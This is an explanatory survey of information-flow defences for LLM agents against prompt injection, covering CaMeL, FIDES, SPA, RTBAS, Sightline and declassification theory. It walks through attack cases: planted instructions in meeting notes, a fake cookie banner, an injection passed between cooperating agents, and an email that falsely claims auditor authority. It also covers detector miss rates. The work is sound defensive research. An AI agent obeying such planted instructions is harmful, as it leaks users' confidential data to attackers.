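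The planner has two tools for working with variables. `query_llm` sends a question and selected variables to a quarantined model and stores the answer in a new variable. The answer's label is the join of the context label and the labels of the selected variables. `inspect` shows the planner a variable's contents and raises the context label to match.

Ana's request could then run as follows, with the name of each new variable on the right:

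```
read_mail()                                  -> #mail
open_sheet("Budget")                         -> #sheet
query_llm("Summarise the budget", #sheet)    -> #summary
send_mail(to="Ben", body=#summary)
```

| Item | Integrity | Permitted readers |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Planner's context, throughout | trusted | everyone |
| `#mail` | untrusted | Ana, Mallory |
| `#sheet` | trusted | Ana, Ben, Chloe |
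| `#summary` | trusted | Ana, Ben, Chloe |

Before the last call, the application replaces `#summary` with the summary's text and label. The summary is trusted and Ben may read it, so both the trusted-action rule and the permitted-flow rule allow the message. Mallory's email had no effect on the summary, because the quarantined model received only the sheet.

The sheet goes into a variable even though it is trusted, because it has fewer permitted readers than the context. If the planner had read the sheet, it could still have written to Ben, but the permitted-flow rule would have stopped it from searching the web afterwards, since the search terms might contain budget figures. Costa and colleagues hid only untrusted data in their experiments and relied on the policies to protect secrets, so they did not measure the benefit of hiding secrets.

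### Trusted calls with untrusted arguments

Suppose Ana also wants the summary to cover the new mail. The planner passes both `#mail` and `#sheet` to the quarantined model, and the summary is now untrusted and only Ana may read it.

With variables, a tool call and its arguments no longer need to share one label. For example, the planner can choose a mail tool and a recipient in a trusted context, while the message body comes from a variable with its own label. Costa and colleagues suggest that a messaging tool could require a trusted call and a trusted recipient but accept an untrusted message. Kolluri and colleagues build this into the trusted-action rule by specifying which of a tool's arguments must be trusted.

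With this version of the rule, the assistant can send Ben the combined summary if the policy requires only one of the two rules to be satisfied. The permitted-flow rule alone would block this, because Ben is not a permitted reader of Mallory's email. The policy effectively treats Ana's request as permission to share the email with Ben, which is reasonable because nothing Mallory wrote influenced the choice of recipient.

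Mallory can still influence the text. Costa and colleagues note that an email could make the quarantined model return an empty summary. An email could also make the model misstate the budget. A company that can't accept this risk can also require the message body to be trusted, but then the assistant can't send the combined summary.

### CaMeL

Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind described an attack that succeeds against Willison's original pattern in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). Willison reproduces their example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025). A user asks an assistant to send Bob a document he requested at a meeting, and the meeting notes contain both the document's name and Bob's address. The privileged model plans the right steps, but if an attacker has planted instructions in the notes, the quarantined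 model may return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. The assistant then carries out the planned steps and sends the document to the attacker.

CaMeL, the system Debenedetti and colleagues built, prevents this by keeping a record of where each value came from. As Willison and Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe it, the system works as follows:

- The planner writes a complete program in a restricted version of Python, using only the user's request and the tool descriptions. It never sees what the tools return.
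- A custom interpreter runs the program one operation at a time, so it can record which values went into each new value.
- Each value carries tags, called capabilities, that record its sources and permitted readers.
- Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy for that tool. The policy is a Python function that examines the arguments and their capabilities, then allows or denies the call and gives a reason.

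Suppose Ana asks the assistant to send the budget sheet to whoever asked for it by email. The planner might write:

```
mail = get_new_mail()
address = query_quarantined_llm("Who asked for the budget?", mail)
sheet = open_sheet("Budget")
send_email(recipient=address, body=sheet)
```

The interpreter records that `address` came from the mail. If Chloe asked for the sheet, a policy that checks the recipient against the sheet's permitted readers will allow the message. If Mallory's email causes the quarantined model to return Mallory's address, the same policy will deny the call. A stricter policy could require Ana to approve any untrusted recipient.

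FIDES can enforce the same rules, because its variables also carry labels. The main difference is that CaMeL's planner commits to a whole program in advance, while the FIDES planner chooses one step at a time. The FIDES planner can also inspect a variable if it needs the contents, which raises the context label.

This flexibility gives the planner more chances to make mistakes. In one test, it requested a list of chat channels although the user had already named the right one, which made its context untrusted for no benefit. Kolluri and colleagues require the planner, before inspecting data, to justify the inspection and list the calls it expects to make next. If it inspects untrusted data without the user's endorsement, the system also reveals all the other variables, since hiding them no longer helps.

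CaMeL also improves privacy. The company that provides the planner's model receives the user's request but none of the mail or sheets, and a smaller quarantined model could run on the user's computer. But someone must write and maintain the policies, and Debenedetti and colleagues warn that users may tire of approving actions.

### Three kinds of task

Hiding data from the planner works only if the planner doesn't need it. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if one fixed sequence of tool calls solves it whatever the data contains. Some of these tasks only move data around, such as forwarding the budget sheet to Ben. Others, such as writing a summary, need a quarantined model to interpret text, but the steps stay the same. In a data-dependent task, the right steps depend on what the agent reads.

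Costa and colleagues sorted the 97 AgentDojo tasks into these three kinds. The last column converts their percentages into a total number of tasks:

| Kind of task | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | All tasks |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Fixed steps, no model needed to read the data | 47.5% | 0% | 18.7% | 19.0% | 26 |
| Fixed steps with a quarantined model | 47.5% | 90.0% | 37.5% | 38.1% | 51 |
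| Steps depend on the data | 5.0% | 10.0% | 43.8% | 42.9% | 20 |

About four in five tasks therefore have fixed steps, although two thirds of those need a quarantined model. The data-dependent tasks include many banking tasks that ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

*Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm* (Chow, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) uses a similar division for web agents. It cites an earlier analysis of WebArena, a set of web tasks, that put 81% of tasks in the first group, 19% in the second and none in the third. That analysis assumed that every website offers a complete set of trusted functions, but Chow and colleagues had to build these functions by hand.

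Chow and colleagues also define the third group more narrowly, because a program written in advance can contain branches. Costa and colleagues classify "If a new email asks for a meeting, add it to my calendar" as data-dependent, since the right tool calls differ from one inbox to another. A CaMeL program can handle this task with an `if` statement. Chow and colleagues reserve the third group for tasks in which the steps come from the data itself, such as finding an email from the boss and doing whatever it asks.

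Ana's possible requests cover all three kinds:

| Request | Kind | Result with FIDES or CaMeL |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Forward the budget sheet to Ben | Fixed steps | Allowed |
| Send Ben a summary of the sheet | Quarantined model | Allowed |
| Send Ben a summary of the sheet and the new mail | Quarantined model | Allowed if the policy accepts an untrusted message body |
| Send the sheet to whoever asked for it by email | Quarantined model | Allowed if the policy accepts any permitted reader as recipient and the address belongs to one |
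| Do whatever the new emails ask | Steps depend on the data | Fails for Mallory's email |

CaMeL cannot write a suitable program for the last request because it would have to list the steps before reading the emails. FIDES can do part of the task. If the company treats Ben as a trusted source, the planner can read his email and act on it while Mallory's email stays in a variable. If the planner inspects Mallory's email, it can no longer take consequential actions.

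### Planning for events in advance

Branches are useful only if the planner has written one for the situation that arises. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that click and type on a screen. The planner never receives the screen's contents, so its program must check for every likely situation, such as a cookie banner that covers the page. These programs averaged about 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 tool calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's programs on AgentDojo.

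An attacker can't add a branch to the program but may be able to influence which branch it takes. Foerster and colleagues placed a fake cookie banner in an advertisement. The program had a legitimate step for dismissing cookie banners, so the agent clicked the fake one and opened the attacker's website.

Programs also fail for ordinary reasons, and the full error message might expose the planner to an attacker's text. Chow and colleagues give the planner only restricted error information for repairing its program. *Kaer* (2026), a design for teams of agents, also lets the planner revise its plan after a failure, and the agents can influence the revision only through the condition they report.

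In *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026) instead let the planner see the trusted parts of the screen. Their system starts with everything masked and reveals only what its rules identify as coming from the site's operator, such as menus and fixed labels. If the rules miss a trusted button, the agent may not be able to use it, but the mistake doesn't expose the planner to hostile text. The planner can work step by step again, though it still can't read a value it needs from a forum post unless the system has a way to make that value trusted.

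### Stored results and later requests

Data hidden from the planner can become a problem again if the agent stores it. In an example from Girrens and Wang, a user asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from Acme and remember the details. The invoice contains an attacker's account number and a hidden instruction. On Tuesday the user asks the agent to pay the invoice. If the planner reads the stored invoice then, the instruction could still redirect the agent.

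The SPA system stores each result's value, label and description separately. The description gives the value's format, its meaning, why the agent obtained it and which request it came from. On Tuesday, the planner receives only the descriptions. Its plan can retrieve the invoice, which still has the label it was given on Monday.

Like CaMeL, SPA writes a complete plan for each request, but it checks all the labels before any tool runs. This is possible because its planning language allows only six kinds of step: retrieving a stored result, calling a tool, asking the quarantined model, displaying a result, branching and looping. Tool arguments can't contain calculations or text templates, so the checker can determine which values each step uses from the plan itself. The checker examines both sides of every branch. A rejected plan has no effects to undo, whereas CaMeL may complete several steps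 before a policy blocks the next.

SPA does not let the planner revise a rejected plan. Girrens and Wang argue that repeated attempts could let hostile content influence planning, or let the planner adjust an unsafe plan until it passed. CaMeLoT, which adds advance checks to CaMeL, does allow revisions. If a program could break a rule, its checker shows the planner a sequence of steps that would break it. Because no tool has run yet, this feedback can't contain text that a tool returned during the task.

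In the invoice example, the instruction never reaches the planner, and a payment tool that requires trusted input would also reject the attacker's account number. But it would reject Acme's real account number too, because that comes from the same untrusted invoice.

SPA is stricter than FIDES because it applies one integrity limit to all of a tool's arguments. If Ana's mail tool requires trusted input, it can't send a summary of Mallory's email. If the tool accepts untrusted input, the integrity check would also accept a recipient's address taken from that email. The confidentiality limit is also set per tool, so it is the same whether the recipient is Ben or Mallory. Girrens and Wang suggest separate integrity requirements for each argument as future work.

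SPA can also hide tool descriptions from the planner, whereas the trackers described so far treat them as trusted. In this mode, a model uses only the user's request to work out which abilities the task needs, the planner writes a plan using those abilities, and a later step matches them to installed tools. A poisoned description can't influence the plan, but about three quarters of test runs failed at the matching step.

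### Subagents with tools

A quarantined model has no tools, so it can't look anything up. If Mallory's email refers to a figure in another document, the model can report this, but the planner isn't allowed to read the report. Zhou and colleagues let a subagent, which is an agent started by another agent, keep its tools while it reads untrusted data, and they use labels to restrict how it uses those tools.

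Their agents' programs are in Haskell. Before a program runs, a type checker rejects it if it uses an operation the developer hasn't permitted. A program may start a subagent, which has no permissions beyond its parent's. Unlike a CaMeL planner, an agent can read a result and then decide what to do next.

The LIO library's `toLabeled` function runs a subagent with its own current label. As the subagent reads data, its label rises but its parent's label does not. The subagent returns its answer as a sealed, labeled value, and the parent's label rises only if the parent opens it. The parent can also pass the sealed answer straight to a tool that checks the answer's label.

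For Ana, a subagent could read Mallory's email, open the budget sheet to check a figure and draft a message. If the email led it to try to send the sheet to Mallory, the mail tool would block the attempt because the subagent has read untrusted data. The parent could then pass the sealed draft to the mail tool with Ben as the recipient, and the tool would check whether the draft may go to him. This design relies more on its tools than Willison's pattern does, because a hijacked subagent, unlike a quarantined model, can use a tool that lacks a label check.

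*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) also lets programs define how models are separated, instead of fixing the separation in the system. A program in its small language can copy a conversation, clear the copy, give it untrusted data and discard it afterwards. The main conversation never receives the data, and the result keeps its label. A developer can build Willison's pattern from these operations, or choose another arrangement.

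### Hand-offs between agents

Hiding data from each planner separately does not protect a team of agents. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three CaMeL agents: a coordinator, one that read a database and one that sent notifications. They asked the agents to send Julie a summary of job applicants over Slack, and planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

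The first two planners never saw the instruction, and their programs did not change. But the coordinator's program put the summary, which still contained the instruction, into its request to the notification agent. That agent's planner treated the whole request as coming from its user, so it wrote a program that sent the summary to Julie and also emailed it to the attacker.

Peters-Gill and colleagues had switched off CaMeL's data policies for this test. Policies in the notification agent might not have helped, because the summary lost its record of origin when it became part of a request. Their solution is to send instructions and data separately. The notification agent's planner reads only the trusted instruction, and the summary arrives as a hidden value that keeps the record of its sources and permitted readers.

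## Estimating which inputs influenced a model's output

Hiding Mallory's email works only if the planner can work without reading it. Another remedy for over-tainting is to let the model read everything, then label its output using only the inputs that influenced it. Suppose Ana's assistant reads both the email and the budget sheet, then writes a summary that uses only the sheet. Under the join rule, only Ana may read that summary. If the application could show that the email had no influence, the summary would keep the sheet's label and Ben could receive it.

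### Dependencies in code and in a language model

In an ordinary program, a tracker can read from the code which values an output depends on, including any condition that decides whether a line runs, but a language model has no such lines to follow. *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) traces the problem to attention, the step that combines information from different places in the text. Attention takes a weighted average over the earlier tokens, or word fragments, for each new token, and normally every weight is above zero. The new token then becomes an input to later ones, so a small influence on one word can spread through the rest of the answer.

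Xu, Li and colleagues (2026) prove in *Sightline* that attention weights alone are not enough to determine which inputs influenced an output. A model has many attention units, called heads. A head can give a passage a large weight but pass on nothing from it, or another head can cancel what it passes on. A passage with a tiny weight can also be decisive, because the passage helps to set its own weight. In one constructed example, a passage has a weight of about two billionths, but changing the passage raises the weight to almost one and flips the output.

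Two other tests also fail. One uses gradients, which measure how the output responds to tiny changes in the input but shrink towards zero when the model is nearly certain of its answer. If the sheet names Ben as the budget's reviewer and the model is almost sure to write to Ben, the gradient may be negligible, even though a different name in the sheet would change the recipient. The other removes a document and checks whether the answer changes. If two documents contain the same fact, removing either one changes nothing, so both appear irrelevant.

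The possible benefit of estimating influence also depends on how many inputs go unused. In prompts from open-source applications, Xu and colleagues found that only 12–14% of inputs had no visible effect on the output, so the join rule was right to treat most of them as influences. An agent's long history probably contains more unused text than a prompt written for one job.

### Regenerating the answer from fewer documents

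Siddiqui and colleagues avoid having to prove that a document had no influence. Their method, permissive propagation, looks for a smaller set of documents that is sufficient for the answer, then produces the answer again from that set alone. It takes a prompt and a set of labelled documents, and works as follows:

1. The application runs the model on all the documents and keeps the answer, y.
2. For each less restrictive label, it collects all the documents at or below that label and measures how probable the model finds y given only those.
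3. If y remains nearly as probable, the label is a candidate, and the search continues with the labels below it.
4. The application chooses a candidate, runs the model again on that label's documents only, and returns the new answer with the lower label. It discards y.

The test in step 3 uses perplexity, a measure of how surprising the model finds a text. If C is the full set of documents and S the smaller one, the label is a candidate when

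perplexity(y | S) − perplexity(y | C) ≤ λ

where the developer chooses the tolerance λ. For Ana, S could be the budget sheet alone. The new summary would be trusted, with Ana, Ben and Chloe as permitted readers, and the assistant could send it to Ben.

The new answer cannot contain anything from Mallory's email, even if the email misled the search, because the model did not receive it in the second run. Only the quality of the new answer is uncertain. If the search wrongly drops a document that the answer needed, Ben gets a worse summary, but its label is still correct for the documents used to produce it.

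Siddiqui and colleagues tested the method on Llama 2 models, which are now old. In one test, each question came with 14 documents, each with its own label, giving 16,384 possible combinations. The search found exactly the right combinations for 86% of the questions. When the researchers instead asked the models which documents they had used, the smaller model was right 2% of the time and the larger one 13%. The search did less well on news articles. Of the labels that could be lowered, it lowered 57% with the smaller model and 39% with the larger one.

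The extra model calls can be numerous. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) puts the number at 16 to 64 per answer for a lattice with four to six levels. Those figures match the number of combinations of four to six unrelated labels. On a simple chain of levels, the search stops at the first level that fails the test, so it needs at most one check per level.

### What the choice of documents reveals

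The second run excludes Mallory's email, but the application decides which documents to use after a first run that included it. Suppose the email says that one budget figure is wrong. The first summary uses the correction, so that summary is no longer probable given the sheet alone, and the application keeps the restrictive label. Ben therefore receives nothing, and if he knows how the system works, he can infer that something he isn't allowed to read affected the summary.

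Mallory can exploit the same step. Siddiqui and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could add distracting text so that the search never finds a lower label, which would block Ana's message. When there are many unrelated labels, an attacker might also influence which documents the final answer draws on. The safety argument for permissive propagation covers what the model reads in the second run, but not how the application chose it.

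The application can close this gap by choosing the label before it looks at the restricted data. Siddiqui and colleagues note that the search is unnecessary when the destination is known in advance. Ana named Ben in her request, so the application can produce the summary from trusted documents that Ben may read, regardless of what the first run would have produced. It must then send that summary even if the full set of documents would have produced a better one, because deciding based on a comparison of the two would reopen the gap.

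This resembles secure multi-execution, an older technique that runs a program once for each security level and replaces any data above that level with dummy values. Searching for a label is more useful when nobody yet knows where the text will go, for example when Ana may later forward an answer to someone else.

### Screening the history before each step

RTBAS, the system Zhong and colleagues built, applies the same idea to an agent's tool calls. It takes a history divided into labelled regions and a limit on the labels each tool may accept. Before each step:

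1. A screener picks the regions that seem relevant to the next step.
2. The application joins the labels of those regions.
3. It masks every region whose label is not at or below that join.
4. The model reads the masked history and proposes a tool call.
5. If the join exceeds the tool's limit, the application asks the user for approval.

If the screener picks only Ana's request and the budget sheet, the application masks Mallory's email and the assistant can write to Ben. If the screener also picks the email, the join of the selected inputs' labels rises and the application asks Ana first. After the call, the tool's result carries both its own label and the call's label.

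Zhong and colleagues built two screeners. One prompts a second language model, called a judge, to identify the relevant regions. The other has the main model draft its next step from the full history, runs a small open model over the draft to measure attention, and passes the scores to a trained classifier. The application discards the draft and generates the step again after masking.

Masking limits the harm from a screening mistake. If the screener overlooks a region with a restrictive label, the model can't use that region, and if it includes too many regions, Ana gets unnecessary prompts. Zhong and colleagues conclude that screening mistakes cannot compromise security, which is true of the content the model reads. But the screener chooses regions after reading the entire history, so its choice can reveal information here too. RTBAS also treats unlabelled regions as trusted and public,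 the same permissive default that Microsoft's Agent Framework had in May 2026.

On 37 tasks involving private data, an agent with the judge completed 40% if the user refused every approval request and 83% if the user approved every one.

### Auditing a finished session

NeuroTaint, built by Cai and colleagues, looks for influence after the agent has acted. It takes a log of the session, including the model's written reasoning, and a list of tools that count as sources or sinks. It builds a graph of how data moved between tools and stores labels alongside anything the agent saves to memory, so it can connect a document from Monday to a report on Thursday.

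For each call to a sink, NeuroTaint first checks the call's arguments for text from a source. It adds a random code to source text where it can and checks whether the code reappears. It then checks for shared wording and similar meaning, comparing the arguments with both the whole source and smaller pieces of it, since a comparison with a long page can miss a short planted instruction. If these checks find nothing, a judge model receives a version of the history with the source replaced by neutral text and predicts whether the agent would still have made the call. If the prediction is no, NeuroTaint reports an influence. It outputs a path from source to sink with a confidence score.

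The random code is strong evidence of copying because it is very unlikely to appear by chance. The other results are estimates, and the score for the judge's answer is just the confidence the judge reports. NeuroTaint also replaces only one source at a time. If Mallory puts the same instruction in an email and a shared document, the judge could correctly answer in both cases that the agent would still have made the call, and the audit would miss the influence.

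### Guarantees and detection rates

RTBAS and NeuroTaint can both rely on a judge model, but a wrong judgment affects them differently. RTBAS withholds the inputs the judge considers irrelevant and regenerates the output without them. This guarantees that their content did not influence the output, provided the choice of inputs reveals nothing. NeuroTaint leaves the agent's action unchanged, so if the judge overlooks Mallory's email, the email may still have caused the call. RTBAS would have the same problem without masking, because the application would mark a message as free of the email's influence although the model had read the email. If a system lowers a label based only on the judge's guess, its protection depends on how often the judge detects influence.

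Sightline makes a more careful guess about which inputs influenced an output. After a model call finishes, it runs the prompt and output through the model again and records how much each attention head attended to each input. A classifier trained on labelled examples converts these measurements into a score for each input, and Sightline drops the labels of inputs that score below a threshold.

Xu and colleagues choose the threshold to meet a target miss rate. For a 1% rate, they score about 1,000 inputs known to have influenced an output, one from each group of software projects, and set the threshold at the tenth-lowest score. If future calls resemble those examples, the chance of missing a real influence is at most 1% on average. At that setting, Sightline removed 44–66% of the unnecessary labels. It can also use an open model to analyze a closed model's calls, with similar accuracy.

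The table gives error rates from tests on agents. A miss is a relevant input that the method treated as irrelevant, and a false alarm is an irrelevant input that it treated as relevant.

| Method and test | Misses | False alarms | Effect of a miss |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Permissive propagation, 40 conversations, larger model | 9.5% of lowered labels | 5% of labels that could have been lowered | The new answer lacks information |
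| RTBAS with a judge, 37 tasks | 10.8% of tasks | 8.1% of tasks | The agent continues without data it needed |
| RTBAS with attention, 37 tasks | 10.8% of tasks | 16.2% of tasks | The agent continues without data it needed |
| NeuroTaint, 400 scenarios | 6.5% of real influences | 8% of harmless scenarios | The influence goes unreported |
| Sightline, 120 agent steps | 3.9% of real influences, averaged by episode | 50% of unnecessary labels remain | The output gets too low a label |

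The NeuroTaint rates follow from its published precision of 92.1% and recall of 93.5% on a test set that was half real influences and half harmless scenarios. The tests differ too much to rank the methods, and the last column matters more than the differences between the percentages. A miss by RTBAS might make the agent try to book a flight without the user's card number, while a miss in a system that lowered labels based on Sightline's scores could send the card number to the wrong place.

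Xu and colleagues retrained the attention screener from RTBAS on ordinary application prompts and tested it on outputs that contained an exact copy of a planted value. It found 42–77% of these copies, depending on the model, while Sightline found all 476. With masking, the screener's errors would make the agent less useful, but they would lead to incorrect labels if the application relied on the screener alone.

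A detection rate also offers less protection against an attacker who keeps trying. If each of Mallory's emails had an independent 6.5% chance of escaping notice, there would be a 74% chance that at least one of twenty would escape. A real attacker could do better by learning from failures. Sightline's stated miss rate depends on new calls resembling the examples used to set the threshold, and an attacker has an incentive to write text that doesn't. In a test with recorded attacks, Sightline let none of 34 attack calls through, but that result is compatible with a true miss rate of up to about 8%, and those attacks were not designed to fool it.

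### Provenance for each argument

FIDES and CaMeL can label each argument of a tool call separately. Two newer systems base their checks on where each argument came from.

*PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compares each argument of a proposed tool call with values the application recorded from earlier steps. If the recipient's address appears in Mallory's email, PACE links the argument to that email. It adds the proposed call to a graph of recorded data flows and searches for a way to cut every path from an untrusted or protected source to an unsafe effect, usually by blocking the call. A separate check compares the call's effects with what the user's request authorised. PACE outputs a decision to allow, change or refuse the call.

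Li and colleagues prove that, under stated conditions, cutting the recorded paths stops the corresponding real flows, but the proof does not cover influences missing from the graph. PACE can recognise a protected value in some standard encodings, but it can miss one that the model has paraphrased, translated or split into pieces. The version they tested also relaxes the rules used in the proof by letting the authorisation check restore calls that the path check blocked, so the proof does not cover every call this version allows.

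Their tests suggest that authorisation matters more than tracing. On a sample of AgentDojo tasks, either check alone reduced attack success from 37.4% to zero, but the agent completed only 13.6% of its tasks with the path check and 64.6% with the authorisation check. On another benchmark, PASB, 31% of attacks succeeded with the path check alone and none with the authorisation check alone. In the full AgentDojo tests, the combined system let through between 0% and 8.1% of attacks in the worst category, depending on the model.

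*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) requires a record of everything that might have influenced each protected argument, and a separate record for the decision to make the call. The second record matters because Mallory could cause harm by making the assistant repeat a payment whose arguments are all correct. A checking program, called a gate, takes the proposed call, these records and a policy. It accepts a protected argument only if every influence on it is trusted or is a value that trusted code has validated for that argument. For example, an error log may supply the path of the file to repair, but not the choice of tool or the statement that someone has approved the repair. The gate refuses the call if a record is missing or ambiguous.

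In 400 test sessions with a coding agent, Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorised argument, effect or call getting past the gate, and the agent completed 231 tasks safely. The guarantee depends on the records listing every real influence. If one model reads Mallory's email and then writes the whole call, a complete record must list the email under every argument, so the gate will refuse the call. The application can keep the email out of the recipient's record by having the model choose the recipient before it reads the email. If the application instead guesses which text influenced each argument, the gate will enforce any mistakes in that guess.

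### Graded labels

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes replacing all-or-nothing labels with graded ones. Each output would carry an estimate of how much information it contains about each labelled input, an idea borrowed from work that measures leakage in bits. One could make these estimates by removing or altering inputs and measuring how the probabilities of the agent's actions change. One could also extend those experiments to the model's internals, hoping to extract a simpler algorithm that an ordinary tracker could follow.

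Ana's summary might then count as 97% budget sheet and 3% Mallory's email. But the policy engine still has to allow or block the message, so someone must decide how much influence is acceptable. A threshold of zero would bring back over-tainting, because nearly every input has some effect on the output. Any higher threshold permits small leaks, which can add up. If the policy allows each message to reveal 5% of a confidential document, twenty messages could reveal all of it unless the application keeps a running total.

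The amount of influence can also be a poor guide to the harm. A recipient's address is a tiny part of a long message, so Mallory's email could contribute very little to the call and still determine who receives the budget. Grading each argument separately would help with addresses, but a confidential decision may be a single "yes" or "no", which even a small influence could reveal.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* objects to security checks that depend on a language model's unpredictable judgment. It accepts probabilistic protection in cryptography because the bounds there rest on problems believed to be hard even for a determined attacker. An influence threshold fitted to past sessions has no comparable basis for its bounds once Mallory writes emails designed to stay below it.

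## Lowering a label on purpose

Even with a perfect estimate of influence, the label check would block some legitimate messages. Suppose Mallory writes in an email that a delivery will cost €2,000 more than planned, and Ana wants the summary for Ben to include this. The email has influenced the summary, so the summary is correctly labeled as untrusted and readable only by Ana. The lattice therefore doesn't allow the summary to be sent to Ben, even though Ana has a good reason to send it.

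Many ordinary programs need exceptions to the rule that secret data must never affect public output. *Declassification*, by Sabelfeld and Sands, mentions a program that publishes the average of secret salaries and a seller that reveals information once the buyer has paid. A password checker also reveals information when it rejects a guess, because the person learns that the guess is not the password.

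Declassification means deliberately letting more people read data, and endorsement means deliberately treating untrusted data as trusted. For Ana's summary, declassification would change the permitted readers from {Ana} to {Ana, Ben}, and endorsement would change "untrusted" to "trusted". Neither operation changes the data, so if Mallory invented the extra cost, the endorsed summary still contains the false figure but is now labeled "trusted".

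Exceptions also weaken what the labels guarantee. Cecchetti, Myers and Arden (2017) point out in *Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* that a system that allows either operation can no longer guarantee that secrets never affect public output. Researchers have therefore looked for weaker guarantees that such a system can still provide.

### What, who, where and when

Sabelfeld and Sands sort the rules for releasing data by four questions:

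| Dimension | Question | Example rule for Ana's assistant |
| --- | --- | --- |
| What | Which information may leave? | Outsiders may learn the budget's total but not its individual lines |
| Who | Who controls the release? | Only Ana may add readers to her sheet |
| Where | Which part of the system may release it? | Only the company's own redaction function may lower a label |
| When | After which event, or how quickly? | The figures may go out once the board has approved them |

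A rule about "what" has a precise meaning. If outsiders may learn only the total, then any two budgets with the same total must look the same to them:

total(B₁) = total(B₂) ⟹ output(B₁) = output(B₂)

Here "output" means everything the outsider sees, so moving €10,000 from travel to salaries must not change a single word of the message. A function that adds up the lines meets this condition, but a language model that reads the whole sheet and writes a paragraph about the total probably does not, because its wording may depend on the individual lines.

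Sabelfeld and Sands add that a permitted release must not hide another leak. If the application declassifies a whole paragraph because it contains the total, it also releases any salary in that paragraph. The application should declassify only the total and then insert it into the message.

In the case of Ana's summary, only Mallory could add Ben as a reader of the email she sent under the decentralized label model. A company would probably set its own rule instead, such as letting employees share incoming mail with colleagues unless the sender has marked it confidential.

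Rules about "where" can name a place in the code or a route between labels. A company could let budget data flow to the mail tool through the redaction function, but never directly. Rules about "when" suit endorsement as well. An application might trust a document only after verifying its digital signature, although *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* warns that a signature establishes where a document came from, not whether it is safe or correct.

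A rule that addresses only one of the questions can still allow a leak. Sabelfeld and Sands describe a shop that may log at most four digits of a customer's card number per purchase. The rule limits what each purchase reveals but not who chooses the digits, so an attacker who can choose them can ask for different ones each time and soon have the whole number.

### Robust declassification

Zdancewic and Myers (2001), in *Robust Declassification*, addressed that kind of gap. As Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, explain the property, attackers may see what a system releases, but they must not be able to affect what it releases or whether it releases anything. An attacker who interferes then learns no more than one who only watches. Their example is a one-line program:

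```
if x then y := declassify(z)
```

The variable `z` is secret, and the attacker can read `y`. An attacker who can change `x` controls whether the program releases the secret, and one who can get some other secret copied into `z` controls which secret it releases. The declassification is robust only if the attacker can do neither.

In *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm*, Kanniwadi and Myers (2026) give an even shorter example of this failure, `p := u * s`, where `s` is secret, `p` is public and `u` is untrusted. If `u` starts at zero, someone who only observes `p` sees zero, but an attacker who sets `u` to 1 can read the secret.

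Now suppose Ana's application offers the assistant a tool that adds readers to a document. Mallory's email says that the company has appointed her as its outside auditor and that she needs the budget. The assistant reads the email, believes it, adds Mallory as a reader and sends her the sheet. To test this release for robustness, keep the sheet the same and change only the untrusted text:

| Mallory's email | The assistant's decision | What Mallory learns |
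| --- | --- | --- |
| Asks about an unpaid invoice | Adds no reader | Nothing about the budget |
| Claims that she is the auditor | Adds Mallory as a reader | The whole budget |

The release fails the test because the outcome depends on what Mallory wrote. It would fail even if Mallory were the auditor, because the assistant would still have relied on a statement that anyone could have sent.

Checking whose authority the assistant is using would not help, because the assistant acts for Ana, and Ana is allowed to share her own sheet. Myers and colleagues likewise distinguish access control, which can stop attackers from declassifying data themselves, from robustness, which also stops them from influencing someone who can.

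The application can prevent untrusted input from influencing whether data is released by refusing any release that the assistant decides on in an untrusted context. Costa and colleagues call their trusted-action rule, used without the permitted-flow rule, a form of robust declassification, because only trusted input can then lead to a release. Ana's message to Ben meets this condition if the planner never reads the mail, since she chose the recipient and the subject before the assistant opened anything.

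Controlling what the system releases is harder. Suppose Ana lets the assistant tell Ben the average salary of a team, using a payroll sheet that Ben may not read. A quarantined model reads Ben's email to find out which team he means, then works out the average. Ben names a team with one member, so the average he receives is that colleague's salary. Ana chose the recipient and approved an average, but Ben controlled what the system released by choosing the team.

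Strict robustness would prevent this by requiring the released data itself to be trusted, but it would also block Ana's summary, which contains text from Mallory. Myers and colleagues concede that strict robustness is too restrictive for many systems, such as a password checker, which has to let an untrusted guess affect what it reveals. Their relaxed version, qualified robustness, lets a program endorse the untrusted input first, so security depends on which inputs the program may endorse.

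### A matching limit on endorsement

Cecchetti and colleagues use a password checker to show how a careless endorsement goes wrong. The checker takes a guess, endorses it, compares it with the stored password and declassifies the result. The programmer has labelled the guess as secret, a seemingly cautious choice that lets faulty or malicious code pass the stored password to the checker as the guess. An attacker who doesn't know the password can then log in. The type systems of the time, which check a program's labels before it runs, accepted this code.

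The remedy is transparent endorsement, which lets a system endorse data only if the person who supplied it could have read it. A password checker may therefore endorse a person's own guess, but it must not endorse the stored password as an attacker's input, because the attacker cannot read it.

Cecchetti and colleagues also describe a sealed-bid auction in which Bob, without seeing Alice's bid, submits "Alice's bid plus one" and always wins. An office assistant could have the same problem. Suppose Ana asks her assistant to collect confidential quotes from Mallory and a rival supplier. Mallory writes "one euro less than the lowest other quote" instead of a price. If a quarantined model reads both emails and fills in Mallory's price, Mallory wins by one euro.

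The application can detect the trick by checking the label's permitted readers. Ana and the rival can read the rival's email, and Ana and Mallory can read Mallory's, so only Ana can read a price derived from both. The application should refuse to endorse that price because Mallory, who supposedly supplied it, is not permitted to read it. If the model receives only Mallory's email, Mallory is a permitted reader of the result and the application may endorse it, but the email contains no price to extract.

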